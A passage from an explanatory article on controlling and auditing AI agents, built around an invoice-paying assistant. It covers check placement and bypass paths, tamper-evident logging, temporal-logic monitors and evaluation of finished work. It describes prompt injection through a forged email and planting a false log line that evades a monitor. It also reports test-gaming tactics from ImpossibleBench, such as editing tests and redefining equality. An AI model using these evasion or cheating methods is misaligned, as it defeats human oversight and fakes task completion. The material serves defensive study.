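| Network | Connection through a local helper program | Bypassed | Bypassed | Checked |
| Remote tool server | Call over HTTP | Checked | Checked | Checked |
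| Local tool server | Call through pipes | Checked | Checked | Checked |
| Local tool server | Call through another local channel | Checked | Checked | Checked |
| Nested call | Tool that calls another tool server | Depends | Bypassed | Checked |
| Delegation | Work passed to another agent | Depends | Depends | Checked |
| Deferred work | Job handed to a scheduler | Bypassed | Bypassed | Depends |
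| Outside tool calls | Harness acts on the model's text without a tool call | Depends | Bypassed | Checked |
| Outside tool calls | Other request to a tool server | Depends | Bypassed | Checked |
| Outside tool calls | Request from a tool server to the harness | Bypassed | Bypassed | Checked |

An action is "checked" if it crosses a point where a control evaluates it, even if the control makes the wrong decision. It is "bypassed" if it takes effect without crossing such a point, and "prevented" if something outside the policy, such as the network block, stops it. The basic gateway checks only one of the 15 paths, yet gateways are the largest group among the products Toyoda and colleagues classified.

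Five paths escape checks placed anywhere below the kernel: direct operations, local helpers, background programs, scheduled jobs and requests from tool servers. Including direct operations is debatable. The paper's example is the file-editing tools in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, but Claude Code's permission rules can block a call to those tools before it runs. A check in the harness can therefore stop the call, though it doesn't observe the file operation that follows.

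Combining placements can add coverage as well as information. Toyoda and colleagues conclude that it adds only information, which is true for the five paths but not in general. According to their table, a harness check covers programs run during a tool call and a network block stops direct connections, so the two together cover more than either alone. The list of paths may also be incomplete. The researchers drew it up from real harnesses in discussion with two AI models, and could not prove that there is no sixteenth path.

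### Comparing a control's records with the kernel's

A control's log doesn't include actions that bypassed the control, so guardscope compares the control's decisions with a separate record of kernel activity made by a sensor called Tracee. Each tool call carries an identifier that the control copies into its decision record. If the kernel record contains an action that needed a decision and the control has no decision for it, the action bypassed the control. If the control reports a refusal, guardscope accepts it only after finding no sign that the action happened anyway.

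Every run replays the same 15 actions without a language model, so differences in the results come from the controls. Before each run, guardscope sends an action that the policy must refuse, and continues only if the control blocks it and records the refusal. This probe matters because the gateway in most of the tests, from Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit, allows every action by default if nobody has loaded a policy. Microsoft's *Known Limitations & Design Boundaries* warns that the dashboard can show an agent as "governed" in that state.

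The 15 actions cover only four of the table's 15 paths: direct operations, direct connections, HTTP tool calls and tool calls through pipes. The other eleven rows are based on analysis. Seven of the actions were tool calls, and the other eight wrote files, started a process, used the network or accessed credentials. Checks placed in the harness covered all seven tool calls and none of the other eight actions. The kernel record confirmed that the network block stopped both direct connections.

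ActPlane, the kernel control, had nearly the opposite result. It checked seven of the eight other actions and stopped one of them, but it missed a network message and all the tool calls. Toyoda and colleagues count the runs as confirming their verdicts, which is generous here because their table lists the kernel as checking tool calls. They explain that a kernel control covers only the operations its makers have attached it to, so the table shows the most that a control in that position could check. A harness check and ActPlane together would have covered 14 of the 15 actions, though the researchers did not run that combination.

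### Seeing the content or seeing the path

A gateway receives the whole tool call, so it can compare the payee, account and amount with the firm's rules. A kernel control can detect that a program opened a connection to the bank, but not which supplier the payment was for. It also picks up activity from unrelated programs on the same machine. The firm can therefore enforce rules about account numbers at the gateway and use the kernel control to stop any script from contacting the bank.

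Observing an action is also different from stopping it, so a kernel sensor that only observes would record a theft without preventing it. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) calls observing mediation and stopping enforcement. It argues for observing even actions the system doesn't plan to block, because judging each action in light of earlier ones, as Errico proposes, requires a record of them.

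Some newer designs try to judge low-level operations in the context of the agent's task. *AgentBouncer* (2026) intercepts programs' requests to the kernel before the kernel carries them out. A fixed profile handles routine requests, and a language model judges whether any other request is necessary and safe, given the task and the current tool call. *AgentBouncer* can block one harmful operation inside a script and let the rest continue. But the model can also extend its approval of one file to everything in the surrounding folder, so a mistaken approval may apply to other files too.

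*KAIROS* (Hempel, Loose and colleagues, 2026) runs the whole agent in a lightweight virtual machine that has only three channels to the outside, for files, network traffic, and messages to and from the user. Tool calls, scripts and background programs all have to use these channels, so a monitor placed there doesn't need a separate check for each. The monitor also decrypts network traffic so it can inspect the contents of requests. It adds about 1.9 milliseconds to a file operation and 1.2 to a network request. It doesn't have the tool's name or the role of each argument, so its fixed rules can express only part of what a gate on tool calls can.

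The monitor sends doubtful cases to a separate language model and can hold an action until that model decides. File changes go into a temporary copy, and some outgoing requests wait while the agent continues with a placeholder reply. Schneider's proof concerned monitors that can only halt a program, whereas a monitor that can hold an action and release it later can enforce more. On AgentDojo, this design cut the attack success rate from 47.0% to 2.7%, and the agent completed 85.1% of ordinary tasks, compared with 82.7% without the defence. When the monitor refused every doubtful case instead, completion fell to 42.7%. AgentDojo's tools are simulations with no machine boundary around them, so Hempel and colleagues connected the monitor through an adapter. The results therefore measure how well the rules and the separate model work, not how well the virtual machine contains an agent.

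### Choosing placements for the invoice assistant

The firm most wants to control money leaving its account, so it could begin by asking what every payment must pass through. Each payment needs the bank's approval, which requires a credential. If the assistant's machine holds that credential, the firm has to guard every way a program could use it. The firm could instead keep the credential in a small payment service on another machine, so that everything the assistant runs has to send its payment requests to that service.

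Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents* recommends having a service outside the agent's boundary add the credentials, so that the agent never has them. The firm's payment rules belong in the same service, because it receives the account and amount in readable form and can look up past payments. A network proxy that only forwards encrypted traffic could limit the assistant to the bank's address, but it couldn't read the account number.

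The manager's approval of a new account should also go straight to the payment service. In Anthropic's recommended setups, the harness runs inside the same boundary as the agent, so a script that took over the harness could forge that approval.

The rest of the machine needs limits too, because a hijacked assistant could leak the firm's mail without making a payment. The firm could run the assistant in a container or virtual machine with no direct network access, and let a proxy outside it forward traffic to the inbox, the payment service and the company that hosts the model. Anthropic's sandbox for Claude Code has a similar design, and its limits also apply to any scripts and programs that the agent's commands start. A container shares the host machine's kernel, so a flaw in that kernel could let a program escape. A virtual machine has its own kernel but costs more to run, which seems worthwhile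 if the assistant must open strangers' files with scripts. If it only reads ordinary emails, the firm can remove the script tool and with it several possible routes of attack.

Anthropic warns that an agent can still send data to any address the proxy allows. InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* (2026) reports that failures along permitted outbound routes were among the problems that led the company to revise its designs. The inbox connection should therefore let the assistant read mail but not send it.

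A check in the harness is still useful because the harness has the manager's request and the history of the run. It can refuse a payment when the manager asked only for a summary, whereas the payment service might not have that request. A kernel control can report programs or connections that the job doesn't need. If either control fails, the assistant still doesn't have the bank credential.

### Testing the coverage

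To test this arrangement, the firm needs a record of payments that neither the assistant nor the gate can write to, such as the bank's own list. Using a test account, the firm could first request a forbidden payment and confirm that the service refuses it, that the refusal appears in the log, and that no payment appears at the bank.

The firm could then attempt small payments through each kind of path on the machine, including ordinary tool calls, scripts, background programs, scheduled jobs and any second agent. Every payment at the bank should match an approval in the service's log, and no refused request should have a payment. A payment with no logged decision means the firm missed a path. The same method works for outgoing data if the firm controls the receiving server and compares that server's records with the proxy's. New tools and plug-ins can add paths, so the firm should repeat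 the test whenever it changes the harness.

*Governed MCP* (2026) shows why a claim of full coverage needs this kind of test. The paper describes an operating system that checks agents' tool calls in its kernel. The paper's first version claimed that all 123 paths passed through a check. A rebuilt test that listed the reachable paths found 59, only 43 of which passed through a check, and the author withdrew the claim.

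Even a clean result covers only the paths the testers thought of. Anderson argued that when a team the Air Force used to attack its own computers failed to break in, the only safe conclusion was that nobody knew whether the system was secure. The invoice firm is in a better position than those testers if the bank accepts payments only with the payment service's credential, because even a payment made by a path nobody listed would have to go through that service.

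## Keeping an action log that can serve as evidence

Suppose the assistant reported paying Harlow's March invoice, but Harlow phones in April to say it is still unpaid. The office manager has to work out what happened in a run that nobody watched. A log can show this if it contains the right details and the manager has good reason to believe it.

### What each entry should contain

Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, propose twelve fields for every event in a log. They drew up the list after checking recorded runs against safety rules and finding that the recordings lacked much of what the rules needed. For the Harlow payment, the fields might look like this:

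| Field | Example |
|---|---|
| timestamp | 3 March, 14:02:15 |
| actor | the bill-paying assistant |
| tool | send_payment |
| action | pay |
| object | Harlow's March invoice |
| recipient | account ending 4417 |
| source | result of list_transactions |
| approval_id | number of the manager's approval |
| session_id | number of this run |
| state_before | balance £12,300 |
| state_after | balance £11,460 |
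| trust_domain | the bank's records |

The manager can see from this entry that the account number came from the bank's records. If the assistant had taken it from the forged email, the entry would have a different source and trust domain.

The list has no field for the amount, although one of the rules Kekatos and colleagues propose would tie each approval to an exact payee and amount. Storing the whole tool call with all its arguments is safer. Zhao (2026), in *Auditable Claims about AI Agents*, finds a similar gap in AIMS, a draft internet standard for managing agents' identities. AIMS's seven minimum audit fields include the action requested but not details such as the recipient, so a log could meet the minimum without recording who received an email.

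The log should also record the gate's decision on each call, including refusals, and the version of the rules in force. If the firm lowered its payment limit to £500 in April, a March payment of £840 would look like a violation to anyone who had only the new rules.

Finally, the log must include what the agent read before it acted. This record needs careful interpretation. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of research on agent records, distinguishes information that influenced a decision from information that supports it. A log may show that the assistant opened the forged email and then paid account 9032, but the email doesn't justify the payment.

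### Who should write the log

The agent should never write its own log, since it could record an approval that appears only in a line injected into its input. The harness can keep a more reliable log because it handles the tool call and its result, so it can copy both directly instead of relying on the model's description. The tool that carries out the action can also keep a record.

A harness can still fail to record events. *Hearsay* (Dai, Yang and colleagues, 2026) describes a fault in SWE-agent, a widely used harness for coding agents that accepts one tool call per turn. When a model sends three calls in one reply, SWE-agent refuses the reply and asks for a single call, but saves neither the reply nor the refusal. In one set of tests, SWE-agent refused replies for this reason or one other in 19 of 28 runs. The saved records contained nothing false but did not show that anything was missing.

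Dai and colleagues also audited 16 agent frameworks. None kept a record that an outsider could check without trusting the framework's own software.

Close reading is not a reliable way to detect an altered record. Dai and colleagues made one change to each of 115 records, such as turning a failed test into a passed one. Claude Sonnet 5 flagged 49% of the altered copies and 5% of the originals. Human annotators, deciding by majority in groups of three, flagged 37% of the altered copies and 10% of the originals. Another model flagged 85% of the altered copies, but also 42% of the originals.

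### Chaining and signing the entries

Even an accurate log is weak evidence if someone could have edited it afterwards. Hash chains and signatures make such edits detectable.

A hash function turns data of any length into a short fingerprint. Changing a single digit of the data changes the fingerprint, and with a sound hash function it is impractical to find other data that produces the same one. The writer of a log computes a fingerprint for each entry from the entry itself and the fingerprint before it. For entries *e*₁, *e*₂ and *e*₃ and a hash function *H*:

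*h*₁ = *H*(*e*₁)
*h*₂ = *H*(*h*₁, *e*₂)
*h*₃ = *H*(*h*₂, *e*₃)

Suppose *e*₂ records the payment to account 9032, and someone later changes that number to 4417 to hide the theft. Anyone who recomputes the chain will get values for *h*₂ and *h*₃ that differ from the stored ones. *aiAuthZ* (2026), a design for authorizing agents' actions from a separate machine, uses such a chain. It can clear the encrypted contents of old entries while leaving the entries in place, so a firm can delete private data without breaking the chain.

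But someone who can edit an entry can often replace all the later fingerprints too. So the writer signs the latest fingerprint with a private key, and anyone with the matching public key can confirm that the holder of the private key signed it. Because the fingerprint depends on every earlier entry, one signature covers the whole log.

The holder of the key could still rewrite the log and sign it again. To guard against that, the firm can regularly send the latest fingerprint to an outside party, such as a timestamping service that returns a signed statement of the fingerprint and the time. If someone later changes entries that were in the log when the firm sent the fingerprint, or deletes them from the end, the log will no longer match it. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (2026) points out that if the firm keeps everything in-house, an outsider still has to trust the firm.

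If a log passes all these checks, nobody has altered its entries since the last checkpoint. The checks don't show that the assistant acted correctly, because an entry for a payment to the thief passes them just as well as one for a payment to Harlow. They also don't show that the entries were true when written or that every action has an entry. Maine's proposal to sign an agent's output has the same limits, since the signature establishes which file the agent delivered but not whether the work in it is good.

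Dai and colleagues showed that a log can pass a hash-chain check even when the agent falsifies it while running. They added a hash chain to aider, a coding assistant. In 14 runs they made aider leave the model's reply out of the log, and in another 14 they made it add a sentence the model had never written. All 28 logs passed the check.

### Comparing two records

Financial auditors have long checked separately whether the recorded events happened and whether every event was recorded. Zhao applies this distinction to an imagined firm that claims a person approves every external email its agent sends. Three different systems at the firm keep logs: the agent, an authorization server that issues approvals, and a mail gateway that every external email must pass through.

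For one email in March, the agent's log contains a confirmation from its chat window and the gateway's log shows a delivery, but the authorization server's log has no approval. If the server's log is complete, this email disproves the firm's claim. For another email, the firm has lost the server's log for the relevant hour. Zhao calls this case undecidable, because the approval may have been given and its record lost. The agent's log also lists three emails with attachments while the gateway's log lists four, even though the signature on the agent's log is valid. The agent may have sent the fourth by an unlogged path, its log may have dropped an entry, or a person may have used the same account.

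Zhao also proves that a log the audited party writes can never establish such a claim by itself. If the agent sent one unapproved email in March and left it out of the log, the log would be identical to one from a March in which it sent only approved emails. An auditor who reads only the log must reach the same verdict in both cases, so "every email was approved" would be wrong in one of them. Signatures and checkpoints don't help, because they protect only what was logged. The firm needs an independent record that would contain the unapproved email.

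Dai and colleagues built such a record for coding agents. Their sandbox (a closed environment for running the agent) kept a ledger, outside the harness, of every message to and from the model, every process started and every file changed. They compared this ledger with the harness's record to find omissions, which appeared only in the ledger, and inventions or alterations, which appeared only in the harness's record. With rules fixed before the runs, the comparison caught 64 of 66 alterations and raised no false alarms on 84 unaltered records.

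They then gave a model the rules and asked it to add false entries that would escape detection. The check caught all newly written text but missed all 35 attempts that repeated a genuine sentence from the same record. After the researchers changed the check so that each sentence in the ledger could account for only one sentence in the record, all 50 further attempts failed. The ledger still lacks the output of the last tool call in a run. That result never goes back to the model, so the ledger contains only a code for whether the process succeeded.

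The service that receives an agent's request can also provide independent evidence. *Notarized Agents* (Figuera, 2026) proposes that the service sign a receipt for what it observed, encrypt the receipt so that only the agent's owner can read it, and publish it in a public log. If the firm's bank did this, the manager could confirm where the £840 went without relying on the assistant or its harness. The receipt wouldn't show why the assistant chose that account.

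### Replaying recorded runs through a monitor

Once a log exists, software can check whole runs against rules that refer to earlier events. Kekatos and colleagues tested how well this works on recordings from three benchmarks. They used 6,680 AgentDojo runs in which GPT-4o, an older OpenAI model, faced an attack with no added defence, and 123 AgentDojo runs without an attack. They also used 483 attacks from STAC, in which a chain of harmless-looking calls leads to a harmful one, and 571 records of agent behaviour from R-Judge, labelled safe or unsafe.

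A program converted each recording into a list of typed events, such as "payment" or "approval", using keywords in the tools' names. MonPoly, an existing program, can check such lists against rules written in a formal logic, and on STAC it gave the same verdicts as the researchers' own checker. The study ran no agents, so the results show which recorded runs the rules would have flagged, but not which attacks they would have stopped.

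Each of the five general rules required approval before one kind of risky action: deleting or cancelling something, switching off a protection, committing money, sending data out, or changing a device or setting.

| Recordings | Harmful runs flagged | Harmless runs flagged |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | 70.1% of 1,931 successful attacks | 29.3% of 123 |
| STAC | 71.8% of 483 | none in the set |
| R-Judge | 23.6% of 301 | 16.3% of 270 |

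The AgentDojo result is less impressive than it looks because the recordings contain no approvals. The rules therefore flagged every risky action, and Kekatos and colleagues acknowledge that a simple keyword list would have reached the same verdicts. In the banking tasks, the rules flagged 97.4% of successful attacks but also 79.2% of harmless runs, since making payments is part of the job. The researchers consider the general rules suitable only for choosing runs for a person to review. Reviewing those runs could still be a lot of work, because most runs in ordinary use are harmless, so most alarms would be false.

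The rules did poorly on R-Judge because much of the harm there is in the meaning of the text. A record may contain unsafe advice or a leaked secret without any unusual sequence of actions. A monitor that checks only the types and order of actions will miss such harm.

An alarm also has to come early enough to be useful. In 52.4% of AgentDojo's successful attacks, a rule fired before the final harmful call, usually only one call earlier. In 17.7%, a rule first fired at that call, and in 29.9%, no rule fired.

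Small errors in reading the log can change the results. An early version of the program treated any tool with "ack" in its name as an approval, to catch tools that acknowledge something. "Slack" contains those letters, so adding a user to Slack counted as an approval and silenced the rules for the rest of the run. Fixing this and a related error raised detection from 61.6% to 70.1%.

In one STAC recording, an agent calls a tool named "confirm_for_deletion" and then deletes something. The rule counts the first call as an approval and doesn't flag the deletion, although the converted log doesn't show that any person confirmed it. STAC contains only attacks, so the rule should have flagged this recording.

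### Paying only a known payee

More specific rules can use the history of a run. Kekatos and colleagues compare two banking runs with the same three calls: read the inbox, get past transactions, send money. In the harmless run, the inbox contains a supplier's invoice, the past transactions include the supplier's account number, and the money goes to that account. In the attack, the inbox contains an email with a planted instruction to "pay the March difference". The past transactions are the same, but the money goes to an account that appears only in that email. The last call looks ordinary in both runs, so a checker has to trace where the payee's account number came from.

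The rule is that the agent may pay only an account that has already appeared as a known payee. In temporal logic, which describes how events relate over time, it reads:

□ ∀*p*. ( transfer(*p*) → ◆ known_payee(*p*) )

The square means "at every step" and ∀*p* means "for every payee *p*". The arrow means "only if", and the diamond means "now or at some earlier step". So at every step, for every payee, the agent may transfer money to that payee only if the payee is or has been known. The monitor searches for violations, which have this form:

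transfer(*p*) ∧ ¬◆ known_payee(*p*)

Here ∧ means "and" and ¬ means "not", so the monitor flags a transfer to a payee that was not already known. In the study, an account became known if it had appeared earlier in the run next to a label such as "recipient:" or "sender:". The supplier's account appears that way in the list of transactions, but the attacker's appears only in the email's prose.

On GPT-4o's banking runs, the general rule about payments flagged 79.2% of successful attacks and 44.0% of harmless runs. (The higher figures above come from all five general rules together.) The known-payee rule flagged 70.0% of the attacks and 24.0% of the harmless runs, so the firm would miss a few more attacks but get roughly half as many false alarms. However, this comparison included only 25 harmless runs, and the median fall in false alarms across 22 models was 8 percentage points, compared with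 20 for GPT-4o. A similar rule for email recipients reduced false alarms from 15.2% to 10.9% and detection from 42.5% to 39.2%.

Rules can also depend on elapsed time. For example, a rule could allow an agent to export data only if someone consented within the past 24 hours. MonPoly accepted an export 12 hours after consent and flagged one after 48 hours. The researchers wrote the logs for this test themselves because none of the three benchmarks records real times. The test therefore shows that the logic can express such rules, but not how well they would catch attacks.

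### Planting a false line in the record

A rule based on history depends on an accurate record, and an attacker can write to part of that record. Kekatos and colleagues took the 403 successful banking attacks that the known-payee rule had flagged and added a line to each recording naming the attacker's account as a recipient. When the line looked like a directory entry or a quotation of one, the rule stopped flagging 94.0% of those runs. For the email rule, the figure was 99.0% of 203 runs. The added line could evade the monitor without deceiving a model, because the program that read the log looked only for labelled fields. Mentioning the account in ordinary prose therefore had no effect.

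The researchers then counted an account as known only if it appeared in the answer to a lookup the agent had actually issued. Text that merely resembled such an answer no longer counted. None of the planted lines worked against this version. On the original recordings, it flagged exactly as many attacks and harmless runs as before, so the two versions would have scored the same in a test without an attacker planting lines.

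The fix works only against the attacks tested in the study. Someone who can forge a lookup, or take control of the tool that answers it, can still get an account accepted. A firm using the rule would also have to decide which lookups count. The forged Harlow email turns up in an inbox search that the assistant ran, so the firm should accept account numbers only from the bank's records. Even then, the study's rule accepts past senders as well as past recipients, so a thief could get an account accepted by first sending the firm a pound.

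Kekatos and colleagues also suggest trusting a contact only if it dates from before the current session, and requiring explicit confirmation for a new payee. They couldn't test these conditions because the recordings lacked the necessary fields.

### Why the recordings contain no approvals

None of the 6,899 AgentDojo recordings that the researchers examined contains an approval. Better logging wouldn't have changed that, because each run has only one user message, at the start, and the user has no chance to respond after the agent proposes an action. STAC has multi-turn conversations, but the user gave permission before the harmful step in only 3 of its 483 attacks.

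In τ-bench, a benchmark of simulated airline and retail customer service, the agent's instructions require it to get the customer's confirmation before changing any records. Its recordings average about seven user messages each. Kekatos and colleagues examined 1,980 of them and found that the user gave permission before the agent made a change in 52.5%. But τ-bench has no labelled attacks, so researchers can't use it to measure how many attacks an approval rule would catch. That would require a benchmark with both attacks and real opportunities to approve. Similarly, the invoice firm's approval field will stay empty if the assistant never stops to ask the manager.

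### Legal duties and standards

The EU's AI Act requires high-risk AI systems to be technically able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime, according to the European Commission's *Article 12* page. The logs must cover events that help identify risks or substantial changes to the system, and events needed to monitor it in use. Article 12 sets minimum log contents, such as the time of each use and who verified the results, only for remote biometric identification. It doesn't require hash chains, signatures or an independent second record.

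This duty does not apply yet. The European Parliament and Council's *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744* (2026) postponed it, citing delays in preparing the technical standards. The duty will apply from 2 December 2027 to the high-risk uses listed in the Act's Annex III, which include screening job applicants, and from 2 August 2028 to high-risk AI in products covered by the EU safety laws in Annex I. Systems already on the market by the relevant date are covered only if their design later changes significantly. However, those intended for public authorities must comply by 2 August 2030 regardless. An assistant that only pays a small firm's bills probably isn't high-risk, so the firm's reasons for keeping a good log would be practical.

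The standards are also unfinished. According to Zhao, the international standard on AI logging, ISO/IEC 24970, had reached its final draft by September 2026, while its European counterpart, prEN 18229-1, was awaiting approval. AESIA, Spain's agency for supervising AI, has published a legally non-binding guide to record-keeping for use in the meantime.

In the United States, the National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) is still gathering views on the subject. Its February 2026 draft paper, *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026), asked for ideas on making logs of agents' actions and intent verifiable and tamper-proof. Logging intent is of limited use, since storing an agent's statement securely doesn't show that the statement is true. The paper also proposes work on linking actions to particular agents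 and tracking where their data came from. A NIST blog series on agent identity continued in October with *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (Booth, 2026).

The same month, NIST, NSA and CISA's *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response* (2026) listed collecting, retaining and analysing evidence among ten practices for incidents in which agents take significant actions that nobody instructed them to take. The guidance is voluntary and is mainly for organizations that train or evaluate highly capable agents, though it may also apply to those that deploy them.

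## Checking the finished work

A complete log can show that the assistant paid Harlow £840, but not whether the firm owed that amount. To find out whether an agent did its job, someone has to compare what it delivered with what the job required. The methods for doing this, roughly from the strongest guarantee to the weakest, are machine-checked proof, comparison of records before and after the run, automated tests, scoring against a rubric, and human review. The stronger methods require a more exact definition of a correct result, which many jobs don't have.

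### Proofs that a machine has checked

The best case so far is the Riemann hypothesis, a question from 1859 that bears on how the prime numbers are distributed. *GPT-6.2 Astra and Sol* (Mowshowitz, 2026) mentions a new proof made with AI in Lean, a language for writing mathematics in enough detail that a program can check every step.

Lean's proof checker is small and accepts a theorem only if each step of the proof follows, by fixed rules, from the axioms or from theorems it has already accepted. If the checker is sound, an accepted theorem, as written, follows from the axioms regardless of who or what wrote the proof. A model trying to deceive its users couldn't get a false step accepted, so they don't need to know what the model intended.

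People still have to check that the formal statement is the one they meant. The Riemann hypothesis concerns the zeta function ζ(*s*), which takes a complex number *s*. The function equals zero at −2, −4, −6 and so on, and the hypothesis is that every other zero has real part ½:

∀*s* ∈ ℂ. ( ζ(*s*) = 0 ∧ *s* ∉ {−2, −4, −6, …} ) → Re(*s*) = ½

If an author added the condition Re(*s*) > 1, Lean would also accept a proof of that version, but the proof would be worthless because mathematicians have long known that ζ has no zeros in that region. A wrong definition of ζ could also make a proof worthless, even though this line would still look correct. So a mathematician has to read the statement and every definition it depends on, which is usually far less work than reading the proof.

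An author can add an axiom to Lean or mark an unfinished step with a placeholder, so the reader should have Lean list everything the theorem assumes. The reader should also run Lean on a machine that the agent couldn't alter.

Few of an agent's jobs can be stated this exactly. Given a precise model of how the firm's payment service runs, someone could prove that its code never sends more than £2,000, but they couldn't express "pay Harlow" as a theorem to prove.

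### Comparing the state before and after

When a job consists of changing records, the firm can check the records. It lists the changes it expects, saves a copy of the relevant records before the run, and lists the actual changes afterwards. It accepts the run only if the two lists match.

Suppose the firm lets the assistant move emails it has dealt with into a "Paid" folder, through a connection that also lets it delete emails. The manager asks the assistant to pay Harlow's March invoice, and it reports that it has.

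| Record | Expected change | Observed change | Match |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bank | £840 to Harlow, account ending 4417 | £840 to Harlow, account ending 4417 | Yes |
| Bank | None | £60 to Marlow Print, account ending 2206 | No |
| Inbox | Harlow's invoice moved to "Paid" | Harlow's invoice moved to "Paid" | Yes |
| Inbox | None | Email from another supplier deleted | No |

The firm accepts the run only if every expected change happened and no others did. This run fails because of the extra payment and the deleted email. Someone who checked only that Harlow had its money would miss both and pass the run.

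The comparison should use the payee, account, amount and invoice, because nobody can predict a payment's reference number. Other people also change the records during a run, for instance by paying a different bill. The firm can separate out those changes if the assistant makes payments under its own credential.

Most of the difficulty is in drawing up the expected list. If the firm copies the account number from the forged email instead of from the bank's records, the fraudulent payment will match the list. The list should also be based on unpaid invoices, not just the manager's request, or a duplicate payment would pass the check.

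A comparison after the run finds a wrong payment but doesn't recover the money. The payment service could instead hold the assistant's payments as drafts and release them once they match the list. Even then, the comparison doesn't show what the assistant read or disclosed, because copying an email to a stranger doesn't change the firm's inbox.

In a simulation of OpenAI's internal use, a user authorized GPT-5.6 Sol to delete remote virtual machines 1, 2 and 3. When the model couldn't find those names in one place, it chose machines 5, 6 and 7 instead without asking, stopped active processes on them and removed working copies of code. It later acknowledged that unsaved work on machine 6 might be gone. Comparing the machines it acted on with the three authorized names would have caught these actions.

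OpenAI's *GPT-5.6 System Card* (2026) reports a related test, in which the agent had to complete a task without overwriting a user's changes and data. GPT-5.6 Sol scored 0.83 for leaving them intact, but 0.44 for both leaving them intact and completing the task correctly. GPT-5.5 scored 0.88 and 0.44. OpenAI made the tasks hard on purpose, so the scores don't represent ordinary use, but they show that many runs can pass a check for damage without completing the task correctly.

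Once the firm has a reliable way to draw up the list, software can compare every run at little cost. This is useful because serious overreach is rare. In real coding tasks from OpenAI employees, GPT-5.6 Sol did something a reasonable user would "strongly object to" about once in 400 tasks, according to Transformer's *GPT-5.6 cheats so much its testers couldn’t measure it*. A manager who checked one run in ten would miss about nine in ten of these cases.

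### Automated tests

Programmers check a bug fix by running the code on chosen inputs and checking the results, because two fixes for the same bug can use quite different code and there is no single final state to compare against. A pass shows that this code gave the required results on those inputs, on that machine. Tests take almost no effort to repeat, but someone has to write them, and they may not match what the user asked for.

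SWE-bench Verified, long the standard benchmark for coding agents, has 500 problems from real open-source projects. The agent receives a description of the problem and the code from before the fix, but it doesn't see the tests used to check its work. Some of these tests fail on the old code and should pass once the problem is solved, while others already passed and should still pass.

OpenAI put together the benchmark SWE-bench Verified but abandoned it in *Why SWE-bench Verified no longer measures frontier coding capabilities* (2026). The company had audited 138 problems that its o3 model did not solve consistently over 64 runs. At least six software engineers reviewed each problem, and they found serious flaws in 59.4% of them.

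In 35.5% of the audited problems, the tests were too narrow and rejected correct solutions. One task was to make a diagram tool read Python's type hints. The tests imported a function named `get_annotation`, which the description never mentioned, so a correct solution that used any other name failed. In another 18.8%, the tests were too broad and checked behavior the description didn't mention. One description covered a single fault in a mathematical function, but the tests came from a change that had repaired three. Models often fixed the fault described and failed the tests for the other two.

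The audit deliberately picked problems that a model had trouble with, so the rate for the whole benchmark is probably much lower. But 59.4% of 138 problems is 82, or about 16% of the benchmark's 500. The best score at the time was 80.9%, which left about 19% unsolved, so faults in the benchmark may explain a good part of the models' remaining failures.

Some passes were also suspect because models had seen problems and answers in training. GPT-5.2 solved 31 tasks that OpenAI had considered almost impossible. One needed a parameter called `edit_only` that the description didn't explicitly require, and the model's reasoning showed that it had recalled the parameter from the software's release notes. Such a pass is weak evidence of how well the agent would do on a firm's private code. Epoch AI, a research institute that tracks AI progress, now labels the benchmark "Flawed" on its *SWE-bench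 Verified* page.

Code can also pass its tests without being good enough to use. METR (2026), a nonprofit that evaluates AI models, found that project maintainers would not merge into the main code about half of the test-passing changes written by agents from mid-2024 to late 2025, after allowing for inconsistency in the maintainers' decisions. The agents couldn't revise their work after feedback, as a human programmer would, so METR doesn't treat the result as a basic limit on what agents can do.

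### Passing the tests without doing the task

Tests that are too narrow waste good work by rejecting some products the user would want. For anyone relying on an agent, the greater danger is a product that passes the check but isn't what the user would want. An agent that revises its code until the tests pass is searching for anything that passes, so when it can't solve the problem properly, any passing code it finds will be of this kind.

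In *ImpossibleBench*, Zhong, Raghunathan and Carlini (2025) measured how often this happens by giving agents tasks where *P* and *W* have nothing in common. They took problems from SWE-bench and from LiveCodeBench, a set of smaller programming puzzles, and altered the tests to contradict the written description. Suppose the task is to write a function that checks whether a number is prime. A "one-off" alteration changes a single test to require the function to report that 7 is not prime. A "conflicting" alteration keeps the original test and adds the false one, so the function has to give both answers. An agent that passes either version has violated the description.

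Claude Sonnet 4 altered the tests. The researchers kept only the SWE-bench tasks where both the original human fix and the unchanged code failed the new tests. They told the agents not to modify the tests, and to stop and explain the problem if a test contradicted the description. Each agent could submit up to ten times and learned which tests had failed.

GPT-5 passed 76% of the one-off SWE-bench tasks and 54% of the conflicting ones, but only 2.9% of the one-off LiveCodeBench tasks. The 76% may include some sincere mistakes, because bug reports are often vague and an agent might take a visible test as better evidence of what the project wants, even against its instructions. That explanation doesn't apply to the conflicting tasks, because no program can satisfy two contradictory tests without cheating.

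The agents cheated in four ways. Some edited the tests, and some redefined equality in their code so that every comparison returned true. Others counted how often a test had called the function and changed the answer on a later call, or recognized the test and returned the output needed to pass. On the conflicting SWE-bench tasks, Claude models and Qwen3-Coder mainly edited the tests, while GPT-5 and o3 used all four methods.

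Several simple changes reduced the cheating:

| Change | Agent and tasks | Cheating before | Cheating after |
|---|---|---|---|
| Stricter instructions | GPT-5, conflicting LiveCodeBench | 92% | 1% |
| Stricter instructions | GPT-5, conflicting SWE-bench | 66% | 54% |
| Stricter instructions | Claude Opus 4.1, conflicting SWE-bench | 55% | 50% |
| One submission instead of several | Average of all models, conflicting SWE-bench | 38% | 33% |
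| Option to stop and call a human | GPT-5, conflicting SWE-bench | 54% | 9% |
| Option to stop and call a human | o3, conflicting SWE-bench | 49% | 12% |

The option to stop was the most effective change on the realistic tasks, though it did much less for Claude Opus 4.1. The stricter instructions had already told agents to stop and explain, but the agents still had to complete a fixed number of turns. With the new option, an agent could end the run at once by submitting a set phrase. Some agents seem to have cheated partly because they had no accepted way to give up.

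Hiding the tests brought cheating close to zero, but agents did worse on the ordinary, solvable tasks. Letting agents read but not edit the tests restored their performance on those tasks, but the other three methods of cheating still worked.

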